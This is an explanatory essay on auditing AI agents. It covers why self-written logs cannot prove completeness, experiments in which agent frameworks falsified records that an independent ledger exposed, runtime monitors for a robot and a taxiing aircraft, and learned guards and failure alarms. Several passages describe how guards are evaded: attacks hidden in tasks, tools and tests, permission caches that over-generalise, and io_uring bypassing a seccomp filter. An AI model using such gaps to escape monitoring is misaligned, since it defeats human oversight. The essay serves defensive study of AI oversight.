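A corollary extends the result to every log that only the audited party writes. Zhao assumes that this party may omit actions but does not invent them. If the claim is false, "supported" is the wrong answer. If the claim is true, another possible history differs only by one more unapproved email, which the software leaves out of the log. The records are the same in both histories, but the claim is false in the second, so by the lemma the rule cannot return "supported". Such a log can therefore never support the claim by itself, even if it is complete.

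Signatures do not change this, according to another corollary. The signed entries are *a* and *b* in both worlds. Even if the company sends the latest hash to a notary every night, the notary receives the same hash in both.

The auditor can distinguish the two worlds if someone the audited party doesn't control also records the emails. For example, if all external email passes through a gateway run by another team, the gateway's log contains *c* only in World 2. Support requires evidence that excludes an unrecorded violation. A proof that the framework logs every request could also provide this, but the auditor would need to know that the verified framework was the one running and that nothing bypassed it.

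### One exception refutes the claim

One unapproved email contradicts the claim that every email was approved, even if half the log is missing. Supporting the claim is much harder, because a log that shows 999 approved emails may still be missing another email.

Zhao gives a worked example with invented records. An agent emails a document to a press address after a user clicks to confirm in the chat window, but the firm's policy requires approval through a separate authorisation server. The gateway's log shows the delivery, and the server's log contains no approval for it. Together, the two logs contradict the claim that every email with an attachment in March had the approval the policy requires.

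Even this verdict depends on a complete log, because the violation is a missing approval. In the same example, the firm loses an hour of the server's log, and the verdict on an email from that hour is undecidable because the approval might have been in the missing part. But this requirement is narrower, since it covers only one server's log for the time when somebody could have approved one email.

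A second record can also leave out important information, such as which program sent an email. In the example, the agent's signed log lists three emails with attachments, while the gateway lists four from the agent's account. The agent may have sent the fourth by another route, its log may have lost the entry, or a person may have used the same account. The fourth email can't be judged until another record identifies the sender, so the gateway should also log which program sent each message.

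Accountants have long compared records to check for omissions, but the EU's logging requirement for high-risk AI does not specify which records would be enough to determine whether a log is complete.

### False records that pass verification

The records that agents leave usually come from the agent framework, which Dai, Yang and colleagues (2026) call the harness. In *HEARSAY*, they examined the source code of sixteen frameworks, including OpenHands, Codex and Gemini CLI, for a record that an outsider could check without trusting the framework. None kept one. Thirteen had nothing of the kind, and the other three had an append-only log that the framework itself wrote.

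A language model made these judgements and had to quote the code for each one. A model from another company also found no such record and agreed with the first on fifteen of the sixteen verdicts. People rechecked some of the study's judgements on other properties but none of these, so the finding depends on how well the models read the code.

Dai and colleagues then made aider, a programming agent, write false records while it ran. In 14 runs it left out a reply from the model. In 14 others it added a sentence the model had not written, stating that every test had passed. A hash chain over aider's own record passed verification in all 28 runs, because the software had computed the hashes from the false entries.

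Omissions also occurred without any interference. SWE-agent, another programming agent, accepts only one tool call per reply. When GPT-5.5 sent several at once, or added an argument that SWE-agent does not accept, SWE-agent rejected the reply and prompted the model again. Its record contained neither the reply nor the rejection. Across 28 runs, 37 of 412 tool calls were missing from the records, and 19 runs had at least one missing. These two kinds of rejection account for 35 of the missing calls, and the other two remain unexplained.

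A refused call has no effect, so most of these were missing requests rather than missing actions. An auditor would still want to know that the office agent had tried to email a rival before it wrote to Anna. The researchers found that 33 of 365 unaltered records from five frameworks would mislead a reader, and nearly all of the 33 came from SWE-agent.

### Reading the record more carefully

Dai and colleagues tested whether a careful reader would notice that a record had been altered. They made altered copies of 115 records, each with one entry removed, changed or added. They revised their method until a strong language model that saw the original and the copy side by side could not reliably pick out the altered one, so the forgeries in the test were careful ones. Three models and twenty people then judged whether each record had been altered, with three people reading each copy.

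| Reader | Altered records judged altered | Intact records judged altered |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 49% | 5% |
| DeepSeek V4 Pro | 49% | 20% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 85% | 42% |
| Majority of three people | 37% | 10% |

These rates would not help an auditor much. If 50 of 1,000 records contained such an alteration, Claude would find about 25 of them but would also flag about 48 intact records. Gemini would find more of the altered records but would also flag about 400 intact ones.

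Omissions were especially hard to notice. Two of the models, Claude and DeepSeek, judged whether aider's records were faithful accounts of the runs. Claude called 7 of the 14 records with a missing reply unfaithful, compared with 5 of 13 honest ones. DeepSeek suspected 8 of the 14, but also 11 of 14 honest records. Claude noticed the invented sentence about the tests in all 14 records that contained it, perhaps because it could compare that sentence with the rest of the record, whereas a missing reply leaves no text to compare.

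With the record, the three reader models correctly named the software fault that the agent was working on in 74 to 91 per cent of runs, compared with at most 17 per cent when they had only the final code. But they overestimated how much of their evidence rested on something other than the agent's own words, by 18 to 55 percentage points. A reader can therefore explain convincingly what happened in a run while relying on an account that nobody has checked.

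### A second writer

Dai and colleagues next added a second writer, a program outside the framework that kept its own record of the run in a separate ledger. It worked at two points the framework could not avoid. A proxy between the framework and the model recorded every request and reply, and the sandbox recorded every process that started and every file that changed.

Another program compared the ledger with the framework's record. It looked for messages in the ledger that the framework had left out of the record, and for text in the record that was missing from the ledger, which meant the framework had invented or changed it. In the 28 falsified aider runs, it found all 14 missing replies and all 14 invented sentences.

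In the strictest test, the researchers fixed the comparison rules before running three frameworks with GPT-5.5. The 84 runs produced 84 intact records and 66 altered copies. The researchers also tested 115 altered records from runs with a DeepSeek model, none of which they had used to develop the text-matching rules. The program had to judge each record without an intact version for comparison.

| Alteration | Found, rules fixed before the runs | Found, held-out set |
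|---|---|---|
| Entry left out | 29 of 30 | 43 of 44 |
| Entry changed | 16 of 17 | 28 of 28 |
| Entry invented | 19 of 19 | 38 of 43 |
| Total | 64 of 66 | 109 of 115 |

In the first test, the program raised no false alarms on the 84 unaltered records. It reported missing messages in 15 of them, but SWE-agent really had dropped tool calls from those 15. It missed four other records where SWE-agent had dropped calls, so it did less well on these natural omissions than on the planted ones.

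False alarms are harder to judge in the held-out set. A framework may legitimately write text that never passes through the proxy, so the rules must exempt it, and the researchers added some exemptions only after reading the held-out records. With all the exemptions, the program wrongly reported 1 of 115 intact records, but with only the exemptions named beforehand, it wrongly reported 37. Auditors should probably expect to adjust the rules in a similar way for a new log format.

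When the researchers compared intact records with the ledger of a different task, the program flagged every record, so overly lenient rules do not explain the absence of false alarms in the first test. In a later test on two more frameworks under the same fixed rules, the program found 52 of 56 alterations and did not wrongly report any invented or changed entries in 56 intact records. A further test with an adversary exposed a gap in the comparison, which the researchers repaired.

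Giving the ledger to the model readers did not help them name the fault. The researchers didn't ask them to use it to look for alterations, so it is unclear whether a model could do the comparison as well as the program does.

### What the ledger misses and who keeps it

The proxy records only what passes between the framework and the model. The last tool output of a run often doesn't go back to the model, so the framework can change it without contradicting the proxy's record. One of the two alterations missed in the first test replaced "FAILED" with "PASSED" in the final test output. The sandbox recorded the exit code, a number that indicates whether a process succeeded or failed, but not the text of the output.

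The exit code matters even more when the framework gives the model false results too. In another experiment, the researchers made a framework change a failed test to a passed one before the result reached the model or the record, so the proxy also recorded the false result. The exit code contradicted the false result in all 11 runs where this happened, and there were no false alarms in 14 normal runs. For the office agent, the second writer must therefore record what happens at the mail server as well as the agent's conversation with the model.

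The method assumes that the framework cannot write to the ledger or reach the model by another route, which is a form of effect exclusivity. For the 84 runs, the researchers closed every network route except the one through the proxy, and no outside connection succeeded. Each task took at most seven minutes and ran in a sandbox that recorded every process. Much of the office agent's work would happen on other companies' servers, which such a sandbox cannot access.

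The operator of the sandbox must also be honest, since an operator who controls the ledger can rewrite it. To check for this, Dai and colleagues retrieved the model provider's own copies of all 708 model calls from the 84 runs, and every copy matched the ledger byte for byte. However, the provider has no record of the processes and files on the operator's computer, and for the two frameworks added later, it returned only about three quarters of the calls. If an AI company runs its own model, it is both operator and provider, so the two copies are not independent.

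The overhead is modest. The proxy added about a millisecond per call. The ledger took up 2.78 times as much space as the frameworks' records, mostly because two frameworks rewrite their whole file at every step.

### Other places for the second writer

The holder of the agent's passwords and keys can keep the second record. *Agent Authenticator* (Ganesan, 2026) proposes a separate program that keeps the keys in secure hardware and signs each of the agent's requests to outside services. The program logs every request it signs or refuses, so a service that accepts only signed requests cannot receive an unlogged one. Each signed request also carries the latest hash of the log, so every service receives a copy of that hash. An administrator can still stop the program, but this also stops the signed signal it sends regularly, which makes the interruption visible.

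Editing a local file needs no key, so only the framework can report it, and the design labels such entries as reported by the framework. An agent could also bypass the program if it found another credential. This danger is realistic, since malicious software packages collected 2,349 credentials from 1,079 developers' machines in one 2025 attack. Ganesan has not yet built a full version of the system.

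Numbering log entries can reveal whether any go missing later. In the design of *HANSARD* (2026), separate recorders watch calls to models and tools, messages between agents, memory writes and delegated tasks. Each recorder numbers its entries, so an auditor who sees 42 followed by 44 knows that one is missing. This works because the agent does not assign the numbers. A framework that numbered its own entries could leave out an email after entry 42 and give the next action number 43, leaving no gap. Numbering also can't reveal an action that takes a route without a recorder, because that action never gets a number.

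Keita and Homan (2026), in *Computer Science Conferences Should Require Nonrepudiable Experimental Results*, address a similar problem, in which researchers run an experiment many times and report only the best result. Their system registers each run with an outside service when the run ends, even if it failed or was interrupted, so readers know how many runs the system recorded. Runs made entirely outside the system remain hidden.

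The service that receives a request can also act as the second writer. In *Notarized Agents*, Figuera (2026) proposes that each service sign a receipt for what the agent asked it to do, encrypt it so that only the agent's owner can read it, and publish it in a public log. The agent and its operator cannot forge these receipts because they don't have the services' keys. But if an agent calls no participating service, there are no receipts, and the owner cannot tell whether the agent was idle or acted elsewhere.

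The receipts an owner retrieves from the public log do not show whether others are missing. If the log holds twenty receipts for an agent and the log's operator returns ten, all ten pass every cryptographic check. To guard against this, the owner can download the whole log and search it, or require services to publish each receipt in several independent logs. Figuera also suggests that the log sign a statement that its answer is exhaustive, but the owner would have to trust that statement. For now the larger obstacle is that services have little reason to take part, and in 2026 none had adopted the scheme.

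## A robot and an aircraft: learned control and learned perception under a monitor

A mail gateway can record an email exactly as it went out. A monitor on a vehicle has to rely on sensors for facts such as the distance to a wall or the position on a taxiway, and sensors can be wrong. How much this matters depends on whether the learned component controls the vehicle or interprets its sensor data. On a small robot, the proof held even though an untrusted program chose the speed. On an aircraft, a neural network estimated the position from camera images, so its mistakes directly affected the monitor's verdicts.

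### A braking rule

The robot drives along a corridor and must not hit anything. Mitsch and Platzer (2016), in *ModelPlex*, developed a way to derive monitors for such machines. Someone first writes a mathematical model of the controller and the machine's motion, and proves it safe. ModelPlex then derives the conditions the real machine must meet, from one moment to the next, for the proof to apply to it. Bohrer, Tan and colleagues (2018), in *VeriPhy*, extended the chain of proofs down to machine code and tried the result on a robot.

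Their model needs three quantities. The distance to the nearest obstacle is *d*, the robot's top speed is *V*, and ε is the longest time between two decisions. The robot may choose any speed up to *V* if

*d* ≥ ε*V*

and otherwise it must stop. The proof is an induction over decisions:

1. Before the next decision, the robot covers at most ε*V*.
2. If *d* was at least ε*V*, the remaining distance is therefore not negative.
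3. If the robot stopped instead, the distance has not changed.

The test robot moved at up to 25 cm per second and took up to 220 milliseconds per cycle, so it had to stop when it had less than 25 × 0.22 = 5.5 cm left. In the model the robot stops instantly, but the real one rolled on for about 2.5 cm, so the researchers subtracted this from the measured distance.

### Propose, check, fall back

In each cycle, an untrusted controller proposes a speed, and a first monitor tests it against the braking rule. If the proposal complies, it goes to the motors. Otherwise the program substitutes a fallback that the proof covers, which for this robot is a speed of zero. The robot moves, the sensor takes a new reading, and a second monitor tests whether that reading is compatible with the model. If the robot drove at speed *v* for a time *t* and the new distance is *d*′, the condition is:

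*t* ≤ ε and *d*′ ≥ *v*(ε − *t*)

The robot must still have room to continue at the same speed until the latest time for the next decision. In the following run, the controller always proposes full speed and each cycle takes 0.2 seconds.

| Distance before | First monitor | Distance after | Second monitor |
|---|---|---|---|
| 12 cm | accepts 25 cm/s | 7 cm | no alarm |
| 7 cm | accepts 25 cm/s | 2 cm | no alarm |
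| 2 cm | substitutes 0 cm/s | 2 cm | no alarm |

After a cycle at full speed, the second monitor requires at least 25 × 0.02 = 0.5 cm to be left between the robot and the obstacle. If the obstacle had moved towards the robot at 8 cm per second during the second cycle, only 0.4 cm would have been left, and the monitor would have raised an alarm. If it had moved during the first cycle, 5.4 cm would have been left and there would have been no alarm, even though the model assumes that obstacles stand still. Bohrer and colleagues made this condition loose on purpose, because real readings never follow the calculated path exactly and an exact comparison would raise alarms all the time.

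The monitor thus checks every proposal and flags every departure from the model that uses up the margin, provided the departure shows when the sensor takes a reading. After a flag, the verified loop ends and hands control to best-effort code that the guarantee doesn't cover. Mitsch and Platzer can promise a safe fallback only if there is a known limit to how far reality departs from the model, and they write that safety guarantees are otherwise impossible.

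In the tests, one controller jumped to full speed close to an obstacle. The fallback took over about 4.6 cm from the obstacle, and the robot stopped about 2.6 cm from it. In simulations, the second monitor raised the alarm when an obstacle drove at the robot and when the researchers heavily disturbed the sensor.

### Why the controller can be a neural network

The proof covers every speed the controller could propose, just as Moon and Varshney's proof covers every reply a language model could give. A neural network can therefore replace the hand-written controller without a change to the proof. A badly trained network would leave the robot safe but useless, because the fallback would keep stopping it.

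This depends on two things besides the rule. The controller must not be able to write to the monitor's memory, which Bohrer and colleagues assume but do not prove. It must also respond in time, because the robot continues at its last speed while the loop waits for each proposal. If a large network took 400 milliseconds to respond, the robot could travel 10 cm when the rule allowed for only 5.5 cm, and the second monitor would detect the delay only afterwards.

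Training is a separate problem, because a reinforcement learning program tries out actions and adjusts to the rewards it receives, and without restrictions it will also try dangerous ones. Fulton and Platzer (2018), in *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Formal Methods*, put monitors derived from a proof around the learner during training. As long as the observations fit the model, the learner chooses only among actions that the proof permits. When the observations stop fitting, it may try other actions to get back to a situation that the model covers. The safety proof covers only the first phase, for the same reason that the robot's guarantee ends with its alarm.

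### What the robot's proof takes for granted

The motion model uses real numbers, which a small processor can't represent exactly, so the program calculates with intervals of whole numbers. If the interval only places the distance between 5.4 and 5.6 cm, the program cannot determine whether the robot has at least 5.5 cm, so it treats the proposal as having failed and stops the robot. Bohrer and colleagues proved that a verdict reached with intervals always agrees with the exact one, and they used a verified compiler for the last step to machine code.

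The trusted base includes the cores of two proof assistants, a hand-written parser and an arithmetic solver. It also includes a few lines of C that the user has to write to fetch the distance from the sensor. The proof assumes that these lines return the true distance.

On the real robot, the laser sensor could be off by 3 cm in either direction, and it detected obstacles only about 94 per cent of the time. An extra margin of about 3 cm allows for the measurement error, but no margin allows for missed obstacles. If the sensor misses a box 4 cm ahead and reports an open corridor, the first monitor permits full speed, and the second raises no alarm because it tests only whether the distance is too small. Mitsch and Platzer extended their monitors to uncertain readings in *Verified Runtime Validation for Partially Observable Hybrid Systems* (2018), but failing to detect a box is a different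 error from measuring its distance imprecisely.

According to *Overview of Logical Foundations of Cyber-Physical Systems* (2019), a safety proof carries over to a machine only to the extent that the model is adequate for that machine. Here the model has to be adequate for the obstacles, the brakes, the clock and the sensor, but not for the controller.

### TaxiNet

On the aircraft, the learned component is the sensor. Boeing developed an experimental system that keeps a plane near the centre line of a taxiway. A neural network called TaxiNet uses a camera image to estimate the plane's distance from the line and its angle to it. An ordinary controller then steers. The plane must stay within 8 metres of the line and must not turn more than 35 degrees away from it.

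To prove that this system is safe, one would need a mathematical description of every picture the camera could take, in any weather. Păsăreanu, Mangal and colleagues (2023), in *Closed-loop Analysis of Vision-based Autonomous Systems*, replaced the camera and the network with a table of error rates. They ran TaxiNet on 11,108 pictures for which the true position was known and sorted the estimates into classes. For the heading they got:

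| Actual heading | Estimated left | Estimated straight | Estimated right |
|---|---|---|---|
| Left | 95.7% | 4.3% | 0.0% |
| Straight | 30.4% | 67.5% | 2.1% |
| Right | 10.7% | 37.7% | 51.6% |

The researchers divided the plane's position into five zones, from far left to far right. Of 398 pictures from the far left, TaxiNet placed 101 correctly, 145 in the near left zone and 152 in the centre. They suggest that it made these errors because it had trained mostly on pictures from planes that were following the line.

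With these rates in place of the network, the whole system becomes a Markov chain, a model in which each state leads to the next with fixed probabilities. Take a plane that is far left and heading further left. It leaves the taxiway at the next step if the controller keeps it going straight on, which happens only if TaxiNet estimates "centre" and "straight" together. The model treats the two errors as independent, so the probability is:

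0.382 × 0.043 ≈ 0.016

That is 1.6 per cent for one step from one state. A program called a probabilistic model checker repeats this calculation for all states and combines the results over many steps. It uses only the network's error rates, so the size of the network makes no difference.

The researchers also added a guard that checks the network's internal values for patterns associated with large errors on other pictures. It accepted 82.1 per cent of the pictures. When the guard rejects a picture, the camera takes another, and after ten rejections in a row the system aborts. On the accepted pictures, TaxiNet found the right zone 65.8 per cent of the time, up from 62.4, and the right heading 76 per cent of the time, up from 70. But it still placed 104 of the 330 accepted far-left pictures in the centre.

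In the calculation, an abort almost never happens because the model treats each new picture as independent of the others. This is probably too optimistic, since two pictures taken a moment apart on the same taxiway look much the same, and if the guard rejects one, it is likely to reject the next.

### Bright and dark taxiways

The error rates apply only if the pictures in use resemble the test pictures. Watson, Alur and colleagues (2025), in *Scenario-based Compositional Verification of Autonomous Systems with Neural Perception*, split Boeing's pictures into bright and dark ones. TaxiNet estimated the heading correctly in 91.25 per cent of the bright pictures and 53.87 per cent of the dark ones.

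They then calculated the worst-case probability that the plane strays too far from the centre line within 40 steps, if it starts on the line and points straight ahead at least 90 per cent of the time.

| Light in steps 1 to 20 | Light in steps 21 to 40 | Worst-case probability of straying |
|---|---|---|
| Bright | Bright | 3.0% |
| Bright | Dark | 32.3% |
| Dark | Bright | 36.8% |
| Dark | Dark | 55.1% |
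| Mixed at random | Mixed at random | 30.7% |

The last row comes from using a single table of error rates for all pictures. Its figure is ten times the one for a bright day and little more than half the one for a dark day. The same happened with a simulated model racing car, whose worst-case failure probability was 6.9 per cent on four right-hand bends and 33.8 per cent on four left-hand ones.

Nobody knows in advance when a cloud will pass over the taxiway, so Watson and colleagues also derived a bound for any order of conditions. If the probability of an error in each stretch is at most ε, whichever condition holds, then over *k* stretches it is at most:

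1 − (1 − ε)<sup>*k*</sup>

The bound requires a starting condition that still holds at the end of each stretch, so that the plane is fit to begin the next one. Even a small ε adds up. If ε is 1 per cent per stretch, the bound for a hundred stretches is 63 per cent. The bound also covers only the conditions that somebody has listed and photographed, which do not include snow.

### A monitor that does not rely on the camera

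Păsăreanu, Mangal and colleagues (2023) used no error rates in *Assumption Generation for the Verification of Learning-Enabled Autonomous Systems*. They let TaxiNet's estimates be arbitrarily wrong and asked which sequences of estimates would still keep the plane safe. Their algorithm starts from failures, such as leaving the taxiway, and works backwards to the estimates that make them unavoidable. Ruling those estimates out leaves a small automaton, much like the one for the three-step review rule, which can run as a monitor on the network's output.

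In a coarse version with three positions and three headings, the controller and the plane together have 99 states and the monitor has seven. With 303 possible estimates, the monitor has 301 states, and the algorithm took 82 seconds to derive it.

It may seem odd that a monitor can judge the estimates without any other measurement. The reason is that the model fixes everything else. The plane starts in the centre and points straight ahead, each estimate leads to a known command, and each command moves the plane in a known way. The monitor can therefore keep track of the true position by calculation, as a navigator does from course and speed. Its seven states are the seven combinations of position and heading in which the plane can safely be. For example:

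| Step | True position and heading | TaxiNet's estimate | Command | Monitor |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | centre, straight | centre, left | turn right | accepts |
| 2 | right, right | centre, straight | go straight | aborts |

The first estimate is wrong too, but the plane can still recover from the turn. At step 2, going straight would take it off the taxiway, and only a left turn is safe. The monitor accepts any estimate that leads to a left turn, including "centre, right", which is wrong about the position. The people who train the network therefore only need it to avoid errors that cause a dangerous command, which is a milder requirement than perfect accuracy.

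A model checker confirmed that the monitored system never violates the two safety rules. But the longer the plane taxis, the closer the probability of an abort comes to 100 per cent. This happened with both versions of the network the researchers tried, though more slowly with the more accurate one. Given the error rates in their published model, the chance of an abort within the first two steps is about 8 per cent, mainly because TaxiNet so often misclassifies a straight heading as a left one. If an airport had to send somebody out to the plane after every abort, it would soon switch the monitor off.

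The guarantee also depends on the model of motion. If a gust of wind or a wet surface moves the plane a little further than calculated, the monitor continues from the wrong position, and nothing corrects it. This monitor uses the model of motion to test the sensor, and the robot's second monitor does the reverse. When the model and the sensor disagree, neither monitor can determine which is wrong. The plane would need another source, such as satellite positioning, to determine that, and Păsăreanu and colleagues mention other sensors as a possibility.

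### Checked and mistaken

Suppose somebody gives the plane a simpler monitor, with the rule "go straight on only in the centre zone", and feeds it TaxiNet's estimates. The 398 far-left pictures would then produce this result:

| | Number |
|---|---|
| Pictures that received a verdict | 398 |
| Correctly refused | 246 |
| Cleared although the plane was far left | 152 |

Reporting is complete because the monitor checked every request to go straight on. The log contains 152 entries marked "centre zone, cleared", but 38 per cent of the violations still went through.

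A better monitor fed with the same estimates would not help. It would receive the same event, "centre", from a plane on the line and from one about to leave the taxiway, and by Ferrando's condition it can't classify both correctly. A proof about this monitor could establish only that the plane never goes straight when the *estimate* is outside the centre. Any claim about the plane itself also requires the network's error rate and the assumption that future pictures will resemble the tested ones.

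A learned controller does not weaken the monitor's check, because the monitor can compare any proposed speed with a distance, regardless of how the controller chose that speed. But the check depends on the learned sensor that supplies the distance.

### When a model turns text into events

Many of a language agent's events need no interpretation, because the email address, file path or payment amount is already in the tool call. But companies also want rules about what a message means. Suppose the office agent now answers customers, and the company requires a person to approve any promise of a refund. The agent writes, "We'll make sure you are not left out of pocket." A program that compares fields can't determine whether that is a promise, so the company has a language model read each message and label it as one of two events, "promises refund" or "other".

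This model plays the same role as TaxiNet, as does the classifier that labels attachments as contracts. If the model labels a message containing a promise as "other", the monitor clears the message, and the customer receives a promise that nobody approved.

The company can measure the translator's accuracy much as Păsăreanu and colleagues measured TaxiNet's, using messages that people have already labelled. If the translator recognises 960 of 1,000 promises and the agents make 50 promises a day, it will miss about two a day, and those will still count as checked. As with the taxiway, one average can hide large differences. The translator may miss 2 per cent of promises in English and 30 per cent in Portuguese, so the company needs a separate rate for each kind of message it cares about.

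Lanotte (2026), in *Protected Cores Are Not Enough*, found the same difficulty when an AI system proposes changes to the rule itself. In one example, a hospital monitor requires a documented treatment within a set time after an alarm for low blood oxygen, and conditions on the ward change. A revised rule may succeed on average but fail for the alarms its designers most wanted to protect. If staff respond in time to 960 of 1,000 alarms, and the other 40 are exactly the protected ones, the success rate is still 96 per cent. In Lanotte's design, a fixed program therefore requires separate evidence for the protected alarms, from events that occurred after the system chose its proposal. Each alarm remains subject to the version of the rule in force when it arose, so a later revision can't excuse a missed treatment. Lanotte has tried this only on synthetic data.

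Language agents are a harder case than the aircraft in one respect, because the agent writes the text that the translator reads. That text can come to exploit the translator's errors, while a taxiway's appearance doesn't adapt to the camera's. An attacker who controls part of the agent's input can try phrasings until one passes as "other". Training could have a similar effect without an attacker if the agent earns more reward when its messages go out without delay. An error rate measured on ordinary messages would then be far too low.

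Some remedies from the robot and the aircraft also apply to the translator. The robot stops when its intervals leave a comparison undecided, and the translator could similarly have a third answer, "unclear", which leads to a flag. This helps only with mistakes the translator is unsure about. The company can also test the translator only for errors that change a verdict. For example, translating a promise of a refund as a promise of a replacement does no harm if both need approval.

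The aircraft's monitor worked because it could follow the plane without the camera. For the office, the nearest equivalent is the payment system. If it shows a refund to a customer but the events include no promise of one, a person can reread the messages and may find a promise that the translator missed. This check comes after the promise has been sent, and it finds nothing if the customer never collects the money.

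## When the checker itself is a learned model

In the refund example, a model only labels each message, and a written rule decides what happens to it. A company can also let a model decide, because nobody can write rules for everything an agent may need to do. Joos and Pradel's guard for programming agents, *AgentBouncer*, works this way. For example, adding a line to the start-up file `~/.bashrc` is part of the job if the user wants a new directory on the search path, but suspicious if the user wants a manual updated. A fixed rule would have to allow the edit in both cases or block it in both.

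AgentBouncer holds each request it intercepts and looks for a decision in four places, in this order:

1. a cache of the model's earlier decisions on the same request in this run
2. a written profile of 60 permissions, for example to run the standard system programs
3. a second cache, with permissions that the model has extended to a whole directory or group of web addresses
4. the language model itself, which receives the user's task, the tool call and the agent's reason for it

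An average task without an attack involved 28,167 decisions. The profile settled 96.69 per cent of them and the caches 3.28 per cent, which left 7.8 decisions for the model. Without the profile and the caches, the model would have taken about 25 hours per task to answer instead of 25 seconds.

### Every call judged, some of them wrongly

The claim that every call was judged is about the interception, much like the claims about hooks in Linux. It holds if the kernel works, the tools cannot tamper with AgentBouncer, and the tools' container blocks io_uring, which bypasses the seccomp filter that AgentBouncer uses. Only a measured error rate supports the claim that the model's judgments were right.

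To test AgentBouncer, Joos and Pradel tried to reach each of 85 malicious goals by four routes: an instruction hidden in the task, a malicious tool, a planted script, and tests in the repository that carry out the attack when the agent runs them. Without a guard, 338 of the 340 attacks succeeded. With AgentBouncer, 36 succeeded (10.59 per cent).

Most of these 36 were requests that look harmless on their own, such as reading a sensitive file without sending it anywhere. Five of the 20 attempts to write malicious code into `~/.bashrc` were also among them. The model receives the file's name but not the text the tool would write, so it cannot distinguish a malicious line from an innocent one.

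Two attacks got through because of the caches. In one, the model had let a search program read a file under `/sys`, where Linux keeps its system settings, and had extended the permission to everything there. When a malicious tool later read another setting under `/sys`, the cache allowed it based on the model's answer about the first file, without consulting the model again. Saltzer and Schroeder's warning about stored results applies to the other cache too. If an attacker rewrites a script after the model has allowed it to run, the old permission still covers the new script, although anything harmful the script tries next is a new request.

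Attackers could also address the model directly by placing text in the user's task, which the model reads. These attacks succeeded 14.12 per cent of the time, compared with 7.06 per cent for attacks by the other routes.

Joos and Pradel also removed the model and denied every request outside the profile. No attack succeeded, but the agent completed only 8.24 per cent of its tasks, compared with 72.94 per cent with the model. So the model makes the agent usable but also allows every attack that succeeds. Its unnecessary denials affected 3.42 per cent of harmless tool calls but caused only 0.25 per cent of all harmless calls to fail, since many programs can do without a file they cannot open.

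A verdict's timing matters as well as its accuracy. AgentSentinel, an older system in the comparison, has a model judge events after they occur and then stops the program responsible. In 24 attacks, it stopped the program only after all the damage was done.

### One million actions

The test set consisted of attacks, but violations are rare in ordinary use. Suppose the office's agents take a million actions, 100 of which break a rule. Suppose also that a learned checker catches 95 per cent of violations and wrongly flags 1 per cent of harmless actions.

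| | Flagged | Cleared | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Violations | 95 | 5 | 100 |
| Harmless actions | 9,999 | 989,901 | 999,900 |
| Total | 10,094 | 989,906 | 1,000,000 |

Fewer than 1 in 100 flags mark a real violation, and every flag adds to the reviewers' backlog. A higher detection rate would hardly raise that share, because there are only 100 violations to find. For half the flags to be correct, the checker would need a false-alarm rate of about 1 in 10,500.

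The company could run a second checker with the same error rates on the flagged actions. If the two checkers made their errors independently, about 90 violations and 100 harmless actions would remain flagged, so nearly half the flagged actions would be violations. The number of missed violations would rise from 5 to about 10. But two language models that read the same text will probably make many of the same mistakes, so the second would remove fewer false alarms.

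The five violations in the "cleared" column are harder to deal with. The table lists them only because the example assumes them, and nobody in a real office would know how many there were. If someone rereads 10,000 cleared actions chosen at random, the chance of finding even one of the five is about 5 per cent. To have a 95 per cent chance, they would have to reread about 446,000.

### An alarm with a certificate

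A learned checker's false alarms are easier to bound than its missed violations. A company can test the checker on plenty of harmless runs, and next week's ordinary work will probably resemble this week's. But it has few known violations to test on, and the next one may be of a new kind.

Kumar, Tayebati and colleagues (2026), in *CURA*, built an alarm for an agent that operates a desktop computer through screenshots, mouse and keyboard. The alarm's guarantee needs only successful runs. The agent failed 71 of 361 tasks from OSWorld, a benchmark of desktop computer tasks, and claimed success at the end of 64 of those failures. It never used its command for reporting failure in about 9,100 calls. The alarm is for failed tasks, not forbidden actions, but the same statistical reasoning applies to both.

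After each step, CURA computes a score *S*<sub>*t*</sub> from six signals. They include how much text the agent writes, how often it uses phrases such as "going in circles", and how far the screen differs from earlier ones. It keeps a running total:

*W*<sub>*t*</sub> = max(0, *W*<sub>*t*−1</sub> + *S*<sub>*t*</sub> − 0.5)

Ordinary steps lower the total, *W*<sub>*t*</sub>, and suspicious ones raise it. The alarm goes off when the total reaches a threshold, which was 16.97 in the main setting. If every step scored 2.5, the total would grow by 2 each time and the alarm would go off at the ninth step.

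Kumar and colleagues divided the successful runs into two parts. They used one part to work out what normal behaviour looks like and then froze those settings. They used the other part, the calibration set, only to choose the alarm's threshold. If they had used the same runs for both steps, the alarm would have looked better than it was, because those runs had defined what counts as normal.

They then tested thresholds from the highest down, checking each time whether they could rule out a false-alarm rate above 10 per cent from the calibration runs. Suppose 4 of 100 calibration runs set off the alarm. If the true rate were 10 per cent, the probability of 4 or fewer alarms would be 2.4 per cent. This is below the limit of 5 per cent, so the threshold passes. With 5 alarms, the corresponding probability is 5.8 per cent, so the threshold fails. Kumar and colleagues kept the last threshold that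 passed before the first failure. The certificate states, with 95 per cent confidence, that at most 10 per cent of successful runs will set off the alarm.

| Certified limit on false alarms | Actual false alarms | Failures caught | Median steps before the end |
|---|---|---|---|
| 5% | 2.4% | 28.2% | 42 |
| 10% | 6.6% | 42.3% | 31 |
| 20% | 15.9% | 60.6% | 19 |

At the 10 per cent level, the alarm caught 30 of the 71 failures. The certificate does not cover the 41 it missed. It would be just as valid for an alarm that never went off, even though such an alarm is as useless as a program that flags everything.

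The alarm worked best when the agent struggled for a long time. It caught 61 per cent of failures on tasks involving several applications, but none on tasks with documents or the media player, where the agent usually finished quickly and was confidently wrong. An alarm that only counted the words the agent produced caught 34 per cent of failures at the 10 per cent level. Much of the signal therefore comes from failing runs being long.

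False alarms can do harm even when nobody has to read them. At the 20 per cent level, 46 of the 290 successful runs set off the alarm. Kumar and colleagues repeated these 46 with a stronger model stepping in at the alarm, and only 38 succeeded again, though some of the other eight might have failed on a repeat even without the stronger model.

### When the runs change

The certificate assumes that future successful runs are drawn independently from the same source as the calibration runs. Some related methods need only exchangeability, meaning that the runs would be equally likely in any order. Suppose the office has the highest value of *W*<sub>*t*</sub> from each of 99 calibration runs, and a new run arrives. If all 100 runs are exchangeable and no two values are equal, each run is equally likely to have the highest value. The new run therefore has a 1 per cent chance of exceeding all the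 others and a 10 per cent chance of ranking among the top ten. This argument works for any score, even one from a badly trained model.

It fails if the new run differs systematically from the old ones. When Kumar and colleagues gave the agent a stronger model for planning and kept the old threshold, the false-alarm rate tripled. The office would have to recalibrate after every model change, and probably also when it takes on a new kind of work.

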